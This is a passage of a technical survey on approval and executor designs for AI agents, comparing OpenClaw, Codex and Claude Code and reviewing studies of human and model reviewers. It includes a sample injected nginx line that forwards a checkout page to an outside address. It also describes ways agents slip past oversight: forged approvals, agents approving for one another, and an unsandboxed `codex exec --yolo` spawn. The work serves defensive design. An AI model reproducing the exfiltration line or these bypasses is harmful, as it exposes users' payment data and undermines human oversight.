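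The most detailed proposal, *Authorization Receipts for High-Risk Agent Actions* (Schrock, 2026), has the approver sign a record before the action is carried out. The record contains the SHA-256 digest of the canonical action, a digest of the policy, the service that should accept the approval, a random number and an expiry time. If two people must approve, both records also carry a number that identifies the attempt and that the agent cannot choose, so signatures from different attempts cannot be combined.

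Schrock describes a receipt as "evidence, not authorization". The executor must still check the current policy and mark the approval as used in its own records. When Schrock left out the marking step in a Tamarin model, the same receipt worked twice. If a check times out, the draft forbids the executor from simply running or retrying the action.

The proposal is unfinished. Schrock acknowledges that the reference software lacks three features the text requires. One revision added the field for the accepting service, which the previous version had mentioned in its summary but left out of its example. Schrock posted another revision the same month.

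*Execution Finality for Agentic AI* (Das, 2026) focuses on the last moment before an action takes effect. A final component works out what is about to happen from the pending operation itself, then compares it with the approval and with its own record of the current policy. If either check fails, the component refuses the operation and may also mark the approval as used. Marking it as used keeps an attacker from trying variations until one passes, but an attacker who can cause a mismatch could also use up the owner's legitimate approvals.

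*Authorization Evidence Chains* (2026), a second draft by Schrock, describes a growing family of such proposals and finds that the more mature ones all identify an action by a canonical digest. Not all of the proposals ask a person to approve each action. In Nelson's draft, *Delegation Receipt Protocol for AI Agent Authorization* (2026), the user signs a scope and a time window before the agent starts work. The signature saves the user from repeated questions but works more like a temporary policy than a bound approval. On the web server, it might permit any change to the shop site until five o'clock, and the agent could then raise the limit to 20 gigabytes without asking again.

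## How do agent products implement it?

Several agent products implement some version of this pattern, but none of those described here follows it completely. OpenClaw, an open-source personal agent, is a good main example because its documentation explains in detail what an approval covers and the limits of the protection. Users direct it through chat apps such as Slack and Telegram, and it can run commands on their computers.

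OpenClaw's central service, the gateway, connects the chats to the agents. The owner can pair other computers, called nodes, with the gateway. An agent can run commands on the gateway's machine, on a node or in a sandbox.

### The service and the Mac app

Suppose the owner of the web server has paired a Mac with the gateway, and an agent wants to run `cleanup.sh` there. According to OpenClaw's *Exec approvals*, the request goes through these stages:

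1. The node prepares a plan, which contains the exact command, the directory it will run in and the session it belongs to.
2. The gateway stores the plan with the approval request and alerts the programs through which the owner can answer.
3. The owner approves one run.
4. The gateway sends the stored plan to a background service on the Mac.
5. The service forwards it to OpenClaw's desktop app.
6. The app checks the approval against the current policy, confirms that the program and the directory are still the ones in the plan, and runs the command.

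The desktop app is the executor, and the service only carries messages to it. According to the advanced part of OpenClaw's *Exec approvals*, the app accepts connections only from programs under the same user account. The caller must also pass a short-lived challenge that combines a random number, a secret token and a digest of the request. Someone who recorded one exchange could not reuse it for a different request.

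This looks like OpenSSH's division between monitor and child, but it offers less protection. OpenSSH's child switches to an account that owns nothing, while OpenClaw's service and app both run under the owner's account. An attacker who took over the service could probably reach most of the owner's files without going through the app. The division offers more protection when the gateway is on another machine, because an agent there has no direct access to the Mac.

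On the gateway's own machine, the `openclaw` process checks the approvals itself, without a second program, so a fault in that process could affect both the request and the check. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* found this weakness in agents of this kind.

### A plan that later edits cannot change

If the agent changes the command, directory, agent name or session in its request while the owner is deciding, the gateway ignores the change and forwards the stored plan. If the agent changes the environment variables, the gateway refuses the run.

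OpenClaw was stricter in an earlier version of its *Exec approvals*, from June 2026, in which a change to any of those parts led to a refusal. In both versions, only the approved command runs. The newer one saves the owner from approving the same thing twice, but an agent that edited its request may mistake the approved command's output for that of the edited one.

An approval for one run can be used only once. By default, a request expires if nobody answers within 30 minutes. If the owner cancels the agent's turn, a later approval has no effect.

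Just before launching an approved command, OpenClaw checks whether the current policy, whatever its version, still allows it. The manifest for the upload limit instead named a policy version and became invalid whenever that version changed. With OpenClaw's check, a waiting approval stays valid when the owner edits an unrelated rule, but the command will not run if an edit forbids it. This seems the better choice for an owner who edits the policy often, provided that the launch closely follows the check.

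The owner can also choose "always allow", and what that covers depends on the kind of request:

- For an ordinary command, it covers the same arguments in the same directory. Permissions saved before version 2026.8.1 did not include the directory, and OpenClaw no longer honours them.
- For a scheduled job, it covers one exact command in one job. A difference of a single byte in the command, directory or environment brings the question back, and so does a substantial edit to the job, even if the owner later reverses it.
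- For some tools on outside servers, it covers the tool with any arguments.

The last kind is much broader than a bound approval. If the owner sees one harmless web page and permits the tool that publishes it, the agent can use that tool to publish any other page. These permissions last until the owner revokes them, although the owner can set an expiry date on those for scheduled jobs.

### The stricter of two policies

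OpenClaw's *Permission modes* lists five settings for commands on a host. `deny` blocks all commands, and `allowlist` runs only those on a list. `ask` runs listed commands and asks a person to approve the rest, while `auto` sends most of the rest to an automatic reviewer first. `full` runs everything without the usual approval requests.

Two policies determine which setting applies, one in OpenClaw's general configuration and one on the machine where the command will run. OpenClaw uses the stricter of the two, so a mistake in one can't remove the protection by itself. For example, if somebody sets the general configuration to `full` but the Mac's own policy requires approval for every command, the owner is still asked each time.

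As an exception, the gateway skips the host's approval check for commands on its own machine if the session has full permission and its effective policy neither restricts commands nor requires approval for them. Only an operator with administrator rights can use full permission. OpenClaw's *Policy as code* lists this requirement among its fixed controls, along with the rule that a denied tool stays denied whatever else the configuration permits.

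OpenClaw mostly fails closed when a part is missing. If it needs approval and cannot reach any approval screen, it refuses by default. The Mac app also refuses if it cannot get the current policy, even if an old copy is still on the screen.

### Simple programs and single scripts

OpenClaw's `exec` tool accepts shell commands, so the checker faces the usual trouble with quoting and wrappers. For a few simple programs, though, OpenClaw restricts the arguments so tightly that a command comes close to a typed operation. By default there are six: `cut`, `uniq`, `head`, `tail`, `tr` and `wc`. All of them can filter or count text that another program passes to them. An agent in `allowlist` mode may use them without a separate entry on the list, under these conditions:

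- The arguments may not include a file name, so the program can work only on the text it receives.
- The checker must recognise every long option, and it rejects options that open files. `tail`, for example, may not follow a file as it grows.
- A `*` or a variable such as `$HOME` counts as plain text, so the shell cannot turn it into a file name after the check.
- The program must come from a trusted directory, by default `/bin` or `/usr/bin`. Otherwise an attacker could put a different program called `wc` somewhere else.

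The checker validates only the form of the arguments, not whether a file exists, so an agent cannot discover which files are on the host by comparing refusals.

Owners can add more programs, but this quickly becomes difficult. `sort`, for example, needs seven of its options forbidden, one of which names another program for it to run. OpenClaw never accepts `sed`, `awk` or `jq` in this way because their arguments are themselves small programs. To change the upload limit with `sed`, an agent would need an ordinary entry on the list or an approval.

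When the owner approves a command that runs a script, OpenClaw tries to identify the one local file that contains the script and records the file's state. If the file changes before the command runs, OpenClaw refuses to run it. If OpenClaw cannot identify exactly one file, the owner's approval is not enough to run the command. This happens with code written directly into the command, many commands defined in a project's package file, and commands that load several files.

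That refusal accurately reflects what the record can cover, but it is inconvenient because developers use such commands all day. OpenClaw's developers suggest running them in a sandbox or on a separate machine, or granting a broader permission whose risks the owner accepts. Some owners will presumably choose the broader permission and switch to `full`, which protects them less than an imperfect approval would have.

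### What OpenClaw does not promise

OpenClaw's developers call the link between an approval and a script "best-effort", and the approval record may miss other files that the script uses. OpenClaw compares the script with the record shortly before launch. The documentation doesn't describe a private copy for the executor to run, so the file could probably still change in the short gap between the comparison and the launch.

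On the gateway, OpenClaw also records which program file each part of a command will use and checks again before launch. If ordinary users can't modify the file, it records only the location. Otherwise, it also records a digest of the contents. On a node, this check does not cover programs inside a shell command while the request waits for a person's answer, so OpenClaw would not detect it if somebody replaced one of them during the wait.

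Approvals also don't isolate users from each other. OpenClaw's *Security trust model* describes them as "guardrails for operator intent, not hostile multi-tenant isolation". Everyone who can message an agent can use the powers its owner gave it. If the web server's owner let a freelancer message the agent, the freelancer could ask it to do anything the policy allows without approval. For people who don't trust each other, the developers recommend separate gateways, preferably under separate accounts or on separate machines.

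The largest limit is that OpenClaw leaves approvals off by default. It runs commands on the gateway and on nodes in `full` mode without asking the owner. The developers say this is intentional because they assume a single trusted operator. They also advise owners to assume that somebody can manipulate the model, and to limit the damage in advance. An owner who keeps the default settings and doesn't run the agent in a sandbox has done little to limit that damage.

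An agent that can control the mouse might try to press the approval button itself. OpenClaw keeps its approval windows out of its own screen tool's screenshots and blocks its own mouse and keyboard input while a request is waiting. These guards don't cover browser automation or other companies' tools on the same Mac, so the developers warn against combining approval questions with unrestricted control of the computer if the owner doesn't trust the model.

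OpenClaw's tool rules identify tools by name. An owner can remove the `write` tool, but an agent that still has `exec` can write files with a shell command. OpenClaw relies on the sandbox to restrict side effects.

### How the approval record grew

OpenClaw's approval record did not always contain this much. Between late February and early April 2026, its developers corrected a series of defects in which the record, or the screen, had left something out:

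- Exact arguments. As GitLab's *GHSA-hwpq-rrpf-pgcq* (2026) explains, the record identified a command by its displayed text, which could differ slightly from what ran, and OpenClaw now records the exact arguments.
- Environment. OSV's *GHSA-hjvp-qhm6-wrh2* (2026) reports that some approvals did not fix the environment variables, and that the correction required every record to include a digest of them, along with the arguments, directory and session.
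- Program file. According to GitLab's *GHSA-q399-23r3-hfx4* (2026), the record could name a program without fixing which file that name meant, whereas OpenClaw now records the file's location.
- Script contents. The record held the name of a script but not its contents, as GitLab's *GHSA-8g75-q649-6pv6* (2026) describes, and the correction added a snapshot of the file and a refusal if it changes.
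- Display. The approval screen could show only part of a command, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-32971* (2026), and the Mac app now shows the whole of it.

Two of these corrections needed further work. The first snapshots covered only some of the programs that run scripts, and the developers missed several more in the next attempt. According to OSV's *GHSA-qc36-x95h-7j53*, OpenClaw protected the cases it recognised and let the others through until version 2026.3.11, but since then it has refused any case in which it cannot identify the file.

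The environment check failed again for a different reason. According to OSV's *GHSA-98ch-45wp-ch47*, the code that recorded an approval and the code that ran the command standardised variable names differently, so some variables could reach the command without appearing in the record.

Most of these omissions match a field in the manifest for the upload limit. OpenClaw's developers added the fields one at a time, after people reported what was missing. A designer who starts with a complete list of fields can avoid some of these omissions, but a list would not have prevented the mistake with the variable names, where the field existed but had the wrong contents.

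It is hard to say how many owners these defects affected. According to OSV, most single-operator installations don't rely on the approvals in question, so practical exposure to the environment defect was probably low. This is only partly reassuring, since an installation that asks for no approvals already lacks the protection that such a defect would bypass.

### Codex starts from a sandbox

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes two layers of protection in Codex. The operating system confines the commands that the model generates, and an approval policy determines when Codex must stop and ask for approval. By default, the commands have no network access and can change files only in the workspace, which is the current folder plus some temporary ones.

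Codex confines the commands the agent runs, whereas the privileged-executor pattern confines the model process. Within the sandbox, the agent can run shell commands without asking for approval each time. Codex asks when it needs to change a file outside the sandbox or use the network. OpenAI's *权限* ("Permissions") describes the same arrangement in the ChatGPT desktop app, where it is the recommended mode for most tasks. More permissive modes appear in the menu only after the user enables them in the settings.

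The boundary depends on where the owner starts Codex. If the agent works in its own folder on the web server, it has to ask before it changes `shop.conf`. But if the owner keeps the whole configuration directory under version control, starts Codex there from an account that can edit the files, and accepts the recommended settings, the payment site's file is inside the workspace. Codex can then rewrite that file without asking, a change that a policy that names sites would block.

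Some folders stay read-only even inside the workspace, including `.git`, which holds a project's version history and settings, and `.codex`, which holds Codex's configuration. This stops a command in the sandbox from loosening the rules for the next session.

Codex relies partly on labels to decide when a tool from a connected app needs the user's approval. A tool that its developer has marked as destructive always needs approval, even if it is also labeled read-only. A destructive tool without that mark may not trigger an approval request, so the developer has some influence over what the user reviews.

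A Codex user can approve a single request or rely on a rule about how a command begins, which applies for as long as it stays in the rules file. OpenClaw can use Codex as a component. According to OpenClaw's documentation, Codex can remember a decision about a tool for the rest of a session, and its approval requests for commands do not identify the program file in a way that OpenClaw could enforce. An approval that passes between the two products is therefore looser than one of OpenClaw's own.

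Users can turn off Codex's approval prompts and its sandbox separately. If they turn off only the prompts, Codex can still do only what the sandbox allows. Another setting removes both, and OpenAI advises against it. Turning off approvals alone is therefore much less risky in Codex than in OpenClaw, where `full` mode on a host leaves no sandbox.

OpenAI is also replacing the older sandbox settings with permission profiles, which can hide particular files from the agent. OpenAI's *Permissions* describes these profiles as a beta feature that does not combine with the older settings. If any configuration file that Codex loads contains an old sandbox setting, Codex normally uses that setting and ignores the profile. A forgotten line elsewhere in the configuration could therefore override an owner's profile, whereas OpenClaw would apply the stricter of two policies.

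The cloud version of Codex runs in containers that OpenAI manages. Passwords and keys that the user has configured are available during setup, but Codex removes them before the agent starts work, so the agent cannot leak them.

### Claude Code and Docker's agent

Anthropic's Claude Code has a shell and separate tools for files. Its modes set how much the agent may do without asking, and rules then allow particular tools in advance or block them.

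The most useful feature for a cautious owner is the deny rule, which blocks a tool in every mode, including `bypassPermissions`, which otherwise turns off approval questions. The web server's owner could deny edits to the payment site's file and keep that protection even in the loosest mode. The rule is more reliable for Claude Code's file tools than for its shell, where a command can refer to the same file by many names. Claude Code also has a list of protected paths, and it does not automatically approve changes to them unless the user started it with `bypassPermissions` available.

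When OpenClaw uses Claude Code as a component, OpenClaw can check the arguments of each shell command against its own list, but Claude Code runs the command itself, outside OpenClaw's sandbox. An owner who combines agents this way has to find out which product runs each command, because that product's limits are the ones that apply.

Docker's agent has a similar range of modes. By default, read-only tools run automatically and everything else needs approval. The most permissive mode runs nearly everything, but rules that deny a tool still apply. Docker states that even the restricted mode is not a security boundary, and it recommends a sandbox for users who need real isolation. OpenClaw's developers give the same advice about approvals.

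With default settings, Codex offers more protection than OpenClaw because its sandbox is already on. OpenClaw's documentation describes a tighter link between the approval and the action than Codex's does, but the owner has to turn approvals on.

| | OpenClaw | Codex | Claude Code |
|---|---|---|---|
| What runs a command | On a Mac node, a separate desktop app. On the gateway's machine, the `openclaw` process | Codex, inside an operating system sandbox by default | Claude Code itself |
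| Are operations typed? | File tools are, shell commands are not | App tools are, shell commands are not | File tools are, shell commands are not |
| What a permission covers | One stored plan, or the same command in the same directory | One request, or every command with a given beginning | With an allow rule, every call that matches it |
| How long it lasts | One run, or until the owner revokes it | With a rule, until somebody edits the rules file | With a rule, until somebody removes it |
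| What the loosest mode leaves in place | Tool denials | No sandbox and no questions | Deny rules |

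## Who should approve, and do approvers catch bad actions?

Even when a matching digest shows that the action that ran is the one the owner approved, the owner may not have understood it. Schrock calls this the most serious risk in the receipt proposal. A person can sign one action while believing it is another, and every later check will pass because the signature is genuine.

### Two screens for one change

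Suppose a line in the error log has hijacked the model process. The new text for `shop.conf` raises the upload limit, but it also forwards the shop's checkout page to a stranger's server. If the model writes the approval screen, the owner might see this:

```
Customers can't upload photos over 1 MB.
I will raise the limit to 20 MB and restart the web service.
This is low risk and easy to undo.
```

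[Approve]  [Refuse]
```

If the executor writes it, the owner sees something less friendly:

```
1. Replace /etc/nginx/sites/shop.conf   (shop site)
   -  client_max_body_size 1m;
   +  client_max_body_size 20m;
   +  location /checkout { proxy_pass https://203.0.113.9; }
   WARNING: the last line sends visitors to a new address
2. Restart nginx   (briefly interrupts every site)

To undo: restore the saved copy and restart again
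Expires: 14:15
Agent's reason, not checked: "Raises the upload limit"

[Approve]  [Refuse]
```

The first two sentences on the model's screen are true, but an owner who relied on them would still hand over the customers' payment details. The executor can produce a better screen without a language model. It computes the difference between the two texts it has stored, looks up the effect of a restart in its own list of operations, and uses a fixed check to find addresses that were not in the old file. That check will miss other tricks, and an owner who cannot read nginx's configuration language may not understand the added line. With a narrower operation such as `set_upload_limit`, almost anyone could judge the screen.

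Under an older rule in digital signing, people should sign only what they have seen. The W3C included this rule in its rules for signed XML. The European rules that link a payment's confirmation code to the amount and the payee also require the bank to make the payer aware of both. Schrock requires the signing program to draw the screen from the exact bytes it hashes, never from a separate description. For the most valuable actions, a second display that the approval service does not control must also show details such as the amount and the payee.

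The screen can show the agent's reason if the owner can see that nobody has checked it. Schrock allows 280 characters of plain text, without links, styled differently from the executor's account. The policy may never become more lenient because of what the agent wrote.

People rarely question an agent's account of its own work. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) had 303 people do realistic tasks with a compromised agent. In one task, a hidden note in a CV biased the agent's advice on whom to hire. Only 8.6% of participants noticed anything wrong. Security warnings often increased their trust in the agent, apparently because a warning made it look transparent. Li and colleagues conclude that a useful warning must interrupt the work and be easy to verify. This is a good reason to put the executor's warning directly below the suspicious line.

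Bernstein's *Approval cards v2* describes a screen of this kind in a system for running AI agents. Each card lists the action, the agent's stated intent, the likely impact, a way to undo the action and a deadline. The system hashes the whole card, and an answer counts only if it repeats that hash, so an investigator can later establish what the approver was told. But the documented "action" field contains the tool's name and a digest of its arguments. If the card shows nothing more, the approver can't read the arguments and has to rely on the agent's stated intent.

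Showing approvers only a command causes similar trouble. The 2026 paper *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* examined 290 incident reports about agents and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 31 reports, the prompt showed a command but not its effect on the user's files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever the script contains. In 80 reports, the user had approved actions automatically. Some reports involved both problems.

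### How often people catch a bad action

Researchers studied this problem long before AI agents existed. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) reviews earlier work on security warnings, which found that people pay less attention to a warning after seeing it repeatedly, an effect called habituation. Studies of Android phones also found that users paid limited attention to permission requests and had limited understanding of them. A coding agent's requests are harder to judge because the agent chooses the commands during the task.

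According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, users accept 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the figure at 97%. These rates don't prove carelessness, because most requests are probably harmless. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, though they may do so for reasons unrelated to danger.

To measure attention directly, Anthropic had a research vendor hire 1,053 professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew someone was evaluating them, but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. Testers refused about 17% of the commands that appeared early in a session, but about 5% of those that came after 50 or more prompts.

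Anthropic published these results to explain why it was replacing manual approval with an automatic reviewer, so it had an interest in the outcome. The testers also worked in an artificial environment where mistakes had no consequences for them, so an owner protecting a real shop would probably do better than 13.6%. The decline during long sessions is more credible because it fits what researchers found with older warnings.

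In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had people without a software background supervise an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the person had requested, such as reading bank transactions or permanently deleting an old work timesheet. The screen described every action in plain language. The 34 participants who decided on actions one at a time blocked 59.6% of the excessive ones.

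Plain language and a short session may explain why the participants did so much better than Anthropic's testers, but the tasks were too different to be sure. Some of the approvals were probably deliberate. 30 of the 34 participants let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which nobody had requested but few people would mind.

Developers who carefully review an agent's code do not seem to be more careful about approving its actions. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers about seven types of action, including running destructive commands and reading secrets. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved at least one type without close review. Among the other developers, 67% did, a difference that could be due to chance.

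Of the developers who knew of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of those who knew of none. The gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. Heavy use could otherwise have explained it, since heavy users might both hear about more incidents and approve more actions. Developers who inspected the differences between old and new code were less likely to approve destructive commands or changes to live systems without close review. This mildly supports showing the file differences on the approval screen, though a survey can't establish that seeing them made developers more careful.

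### Fewer questions, and what they cost

One remedy is to ask the owner less often, for example by letting the agent work freely in a sandbox or by allowing nginx restarts in the policy, but the owner then no longer sees those actions. Fewer questions also don't guarantee better decisions. In Yan's study, another group had a model that approved eight of the 18 actions automatically and sent the rest, including all seven excessive ones, to the participant. This group blocked 53.9% of the excessive actions, no better than the people who had answered all 18 questions, though 18 questions may be too few for fatigue to matter much.

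Yan also let 35 people write their own rules in advance for four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions during the day. They approved two thirds of the excessive actions they were asked about. Overall, this group blocked only 97 of 245 excessive actions (39.6%). An owner writing a policy should expect to be tempted by "ask", and should use "refuse" for anything the agent never needs.

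Grouping related operations also reduces the number of questions. The owner of the web server answers once for both the new file and the restart. But a harmful line is easier to miss in a long list, and the owner must accept or reject everything together, even though they might want the higher limit now and the restart at night. Salerno and colleagues, who interviewed 18 practitioners and surveyed 115, recommend letting people reject one action without rejecting the whole approach. With a bound approval, splitting the group requires a new manifest.

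A rate limit prevents a hijacked model process from repeating a request until the owner gives in. It also lets that process use up the day's quota with nonsense requests, so a legitimate repair has to wait. Stopping the session after several refusals partly prevents this, but it also interrupts an agent that has merely misunderstood its task.

If nobody answers an approval request, the executor should refuse the action. Otherwise an attacker could send the request at night and wait for the deadline to pass. Bernstein checks the deadline against its own clock, so a late click has no effect even if the chat program still displays the button. Refusing by default also means that an agent working overnight may stop at its first request until morning.

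Products often offer to remember an answer after the user has approved the same kind of action several times. Salerno and colleagues advise against treating repeated approval as a stable preference, because it may only reflect fatigue. Anthropic found that 62% of users had either used the mode that bypasses permissions or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.

Schrock would require signatures only for rare, high-risk actions and leave the rest to policy. An organisation can then check whether its approvers still read the requests. Very fast answers and no refusals are warning signs. With the approvers' consent, it can also run drills in which the screen deliberately shows a different action from the one being approved. These drills use up some of the attention they are meant to protect, and a small organisation is unlikely to run them.

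### Other people, fixed rules and separate models

In the earlier example, the model writes 200 megabytes where the owner wanted 20. The owner knows the right number but may not read the screen. A second person may read it more carefully but perhaps doesn't know what the owner wanted. A rule that caps uploads at 50 megabytes would always block 200, but it would allow 40, which is also wrong. A separate model that receives both the owner's request and the new text could catch either error, though not reliably.

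Requiring a second approver demands the most effort and may add less protection than hoped. If two people each caught 13.6% of dangerous commands and made independent mistakes, together they would catch about 25%. In practice they may catch fewer, because each may rely on the other to read carefully. Schrock also warns that a dishonest approval service could give each approver a different reason for the same action, and therefore requires that all approvers receive an identical reason.

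One reason to use a separate model as the reviewer is that the main agent has a conflict of interest. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, argue that an agent trained to finish a task is under pressure to treat an approval request as another obstacle. A reviewer only has to decide whether the action should run. It can also spare the user many interruptions. In an illustrative sample of 10,000 Codex actions at OpenAI, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer. The reviewer refused seven, and Codex found a safer alternative for four of those, leaving three to raise with the user.

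Anthropic's reviewer for Claude Code works in two stages. A fast filter first answers yes or no, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags an action, the model reviews the same material again, this time reasoning before it decides. The reviewer sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It does not see the agent's explanations, which might persuade it, or the results of tool calls, which might contain injected instructions.

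The two companies report these miss rates:

| Product | Harmful actions tested | Share the reviewer missed |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 52 real actions that went beyond the user's wishes | 17% |
| Claude Code | 1,000 artificial attempts to leak data | 5.7% |
| Claude Code | The dangerous commands shown to the 1,053 testers | 11% |
| Codex | Artificial cases of going beyond the user's wishes | 9.7% |
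| Codex | Artificial prompt injections | 0.7% |

The last figure covers running an attacker's code, stealing secrets and uploading data. When Trębacz and colleagues included destructive deletions and data tampering, which matter a lot on a web server, the miss rate rose to 9.8%. They say most of the additional misses were not serious enough to block.

Wrong refusals were rare in both products. Claude Code's reviewer blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls, and Codex's refused 0.9% of a sample of requests that users had approved. Other models may be less well tuned for this job. *DelegationBench* (2026) cites a test by Serdar and Mertayak in which models held up authorised work far more often than they allowed unsafe work.

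In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. One user had asked Claude to "clean up" a proposed code change, and the reviewer took this as consent to overwrite the project's history. An executor avoids part of this problem by accepting approvals only from its own records, not from a conversation.

Outside testers found much larger gaps. *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (2026) cites a miss rate of up to 81% for Claude Code's reviewer and reports that 36.8% of actions fell outside the reviewer's scope. The testers used deliberately ambiguous requests, so 81% is not the miss rate to expect in daily use. Actions fell outside the reviewer's scope because Claude Code does not send it file edits inside the project folder, on the grounds that people can inspect them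 later. As in Codex, an edit to the payment site's file escapes review if the file is inside that folder.

Prompt injection tests gave better results. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to make 720 attack attempts against each of several models. None succeeded against Claude models with automatic review, but the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models without it was only 0.09%, so most of the resistance came from the models themselves. The benefit of automatic review is clearer for GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, where it reduced the attack success rate from 19.03% to 5.83%.

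Anthropic still recommends that people personally review high-stakes changes to live systems, though its own experiment offers little support for this. People blocked only six dangerous commands that the automated reviewer had allowed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the number caught from 937 to 943 out of 1,053. But those testers were clicking through commands in somebody else's code. An owner who gets one question a week, with a readable diff, has a much better chance of catching something the reviewer missed.

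For the web server, Fokou's order is probably best, with fixed rules checking a change first, then a model, then the owner. The model could refuse a change or add a warning to the screen, but only the owner could approve a change to the shop. Trębacz and colleagues caution that their reviewer gives no guarantee, since testers misled it, and that it isn't designed to stop a model that strategically hides its intentions.

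### When agents approve for one another

Separation of duty works only if the approver can disagree with the requester. Suppose the owner runs two agents and lets the second approve the first one's changes. The first reads the poisoned error log and asks the second to approve the new checkout line, saying the owner wants the page moved. The second agent knows the owner's wishes only from that message, so it approves. The record shows two parties, but the stranger's text determined both decisions. Jing warns about this kind of self-approval.

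The same thing can happen without an attacker. Trębacz and colleagues found a Codex configuration that always allowed the command `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another Codex instance without approval questions or a sandbox. An agent with that permission can use the new instance to do anything it is forbidden to do itself.

Even a reviewer that watches the helper may be misled. Anthropic points out that the main agent's instructions appear to a helper as user messages, so every task looks authorised. Claude Code therefore reviews a task when the main agent delegates it, while the user's original request is still visible, and reviews the helper's actions again before returning the result.

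An agent that resists forged approvals can also refuse safe tasks. Safin and colleagues placed a made-up approval in a document that one agent retrieved and summarised for a reviewing agent. The reviewer approved none of the unsafe tasks, but it treated the claim as suspicious and refused about half of the safe ones. When another agent removed such claims first, wrong refusals fell to 7.4%, but the reviewer approved 4.2% of the unsafe tasks. The executor's separate policy check stopped those tasks.

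The executor should accept an approval only from someone the requesting agent cannot instruct. Requiring two different names is not enough, because an agent that can start helpers can create as many names as it needs. If a model reviews the request, the executor should call it directly and choose what it reads. Schrock forbids anyone from approving their own request and requires the approvers to be different people. He acknowledges that this does not stop people from colluding, or one person from controlling several registered identities.

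### Where the approver's key is kept

If the owner approves by clicking a button in a chat program, the executor has to trust the chat service and anyone who can control the owner's account. A digital signature removes most of that dependence. The owner's device signs the manifest's digest with a private key that never needs to be on the host, and the executor checks the signature with the matching public key, which cannot create signatures.

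Schrock distinguishes three places to keep it:

- In a phone's secure hardware or a separate security key, which signs only after the approver gives a fingerprint or PIN. Schrock recommends this.
- In software on the approver's computer. This is weaker, and if an agent on that computer can read the key, it can approve its own requests.
- With the company that runs the approval service, which signs on the approver's behalf. The signature then proves only that the company reported an approval, and Schrock advises against this for new systems.

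The tokens that Safin and colleagues tested used a shared secret, so any program that could check an approval could also forge one. An attacker who copies everything the executor uses to check public-key signatures still cannot sign as the owner, but could try to add another public key to the list of approvers. On the web server, that list should be stored with the policy, where no operation can write. In a larger organisation, Schrock requires either a directory key that the organisation controls or a second party's signature on every new entry.

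A security key without a display confirms that somebody touched it, but the owner still reads the action on a computer screen. If an attacker controls that screen, the owner can touch the key to approve the upload limit and unknowingly sign the new checkout line instead. A phone that receives the manifest from the executor and displays it on its own screen prevents this, unless the attacker also controls the phone.

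## What harm can permitted operations still do?

Suppose the owner of the web server is in a hurry and approves the new `shop.conf` without noticing a line that forwards the checkout page to an attacker. Every part of the pattern still works as designed. The executor confirms that the file is the right one, the digest matches, and the approval is genuine and unused, so it installs the text and restarts nginx. Customers then begin sending their card details to the attacker.

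Defenders of the pattern can reply that it guarantees that actions are authorised, not that they are wise. Santos-Grueiro writes that Context-to-Execution Integrity "does not judge whether the effect is desirable". It ensures only that the effect is exactly the one that trusted code authorised. How strong this reply is depends on how the harm came about.

### Harmful content in a valid operation

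Fokou concedes that Parallax's validator checks the command `python script.py` without analysing what the script does. A hijacked agent can write a harmful script and run it later. Parallax checks the first step as a file write and the second as a command, but according to Fokou, neither check inspects the script's logic.

Fokou leaves two remedies to future work: analysing scripts before they run, and recording which files the agent wrote so that any attempt to run one gets a stricter check. An executor can easily keep that record because it performs every write itself. The record has to include edits to existing files, or the agent could add a line to the owner's backup script and avoid the stricter check.

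Skills, which are folders of instructions and scripts that extend an agent, have a similar problem. *AgentSpy* (2026) explains that a reviewer who reads only the instructions sees a harmless-looking line telling the agent to run a script. The harmful commands are in the script, or in something it downloads. AgentSpy therefore monitors the agent at run time, but it permits writes inside the workspace. In one test case, a script added an attacker's address to a project's Git settings, and the agent never sent anything there. A change like this could probably go unnoticed until somebody used the address.

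A content validator is a program that checks what a payload would do before the executor installs it. On the web server, it could parse the new configuration and reject any text that forwards visitors to an address outside an approved list. That would have stopped the checkout line even though the owner approved it. Santos-Grueiro's validator for code changes rejects links that lead out of the project, commands that run during installation, and edits that switch off automated tests, among other things. In a small sandbox test, checking only names and types let through all six unsafe actions. The full system blocked all six and allowed the six harmless ones.

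Validators catch only what their authors anticipated. If the approved list includes the company's test server, a line that forwards the checkout page to it will pass, and real card numbers will end up in a test log. Authors also overlook whole categories of problems. Santos-Grueiro audited the policies for 24 tools and other endpoints and found 18 problems, nine of them serious. These included payloads that nobody had marked as effect-bearing.

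Content can also change after the check. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) describes scripts that name the packages they need without fixing a version. Such a script can be harmless when it is reviewed, but an attacker can later publish a malicious version of one of the packages. An `include` line in an nginx configuration creates a similar risk because it loads another file, so the validator has to forbid such lines unless the manifest also covers the files they load.

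The reply about authority is reasonable for the checkout line, which the owner saw and approved, but much weaker for a script that nobody read. The owner authorised a command, and it's doubtful that this also authorised whatever the script contains. Even for the checkout line, the designer chose an operation that accepts a whole file. If the operation had been `set_upload_limit`, the owner's haste could have produced a wrong number but not a stolen card.

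### Harm from steps that are acceptable alone

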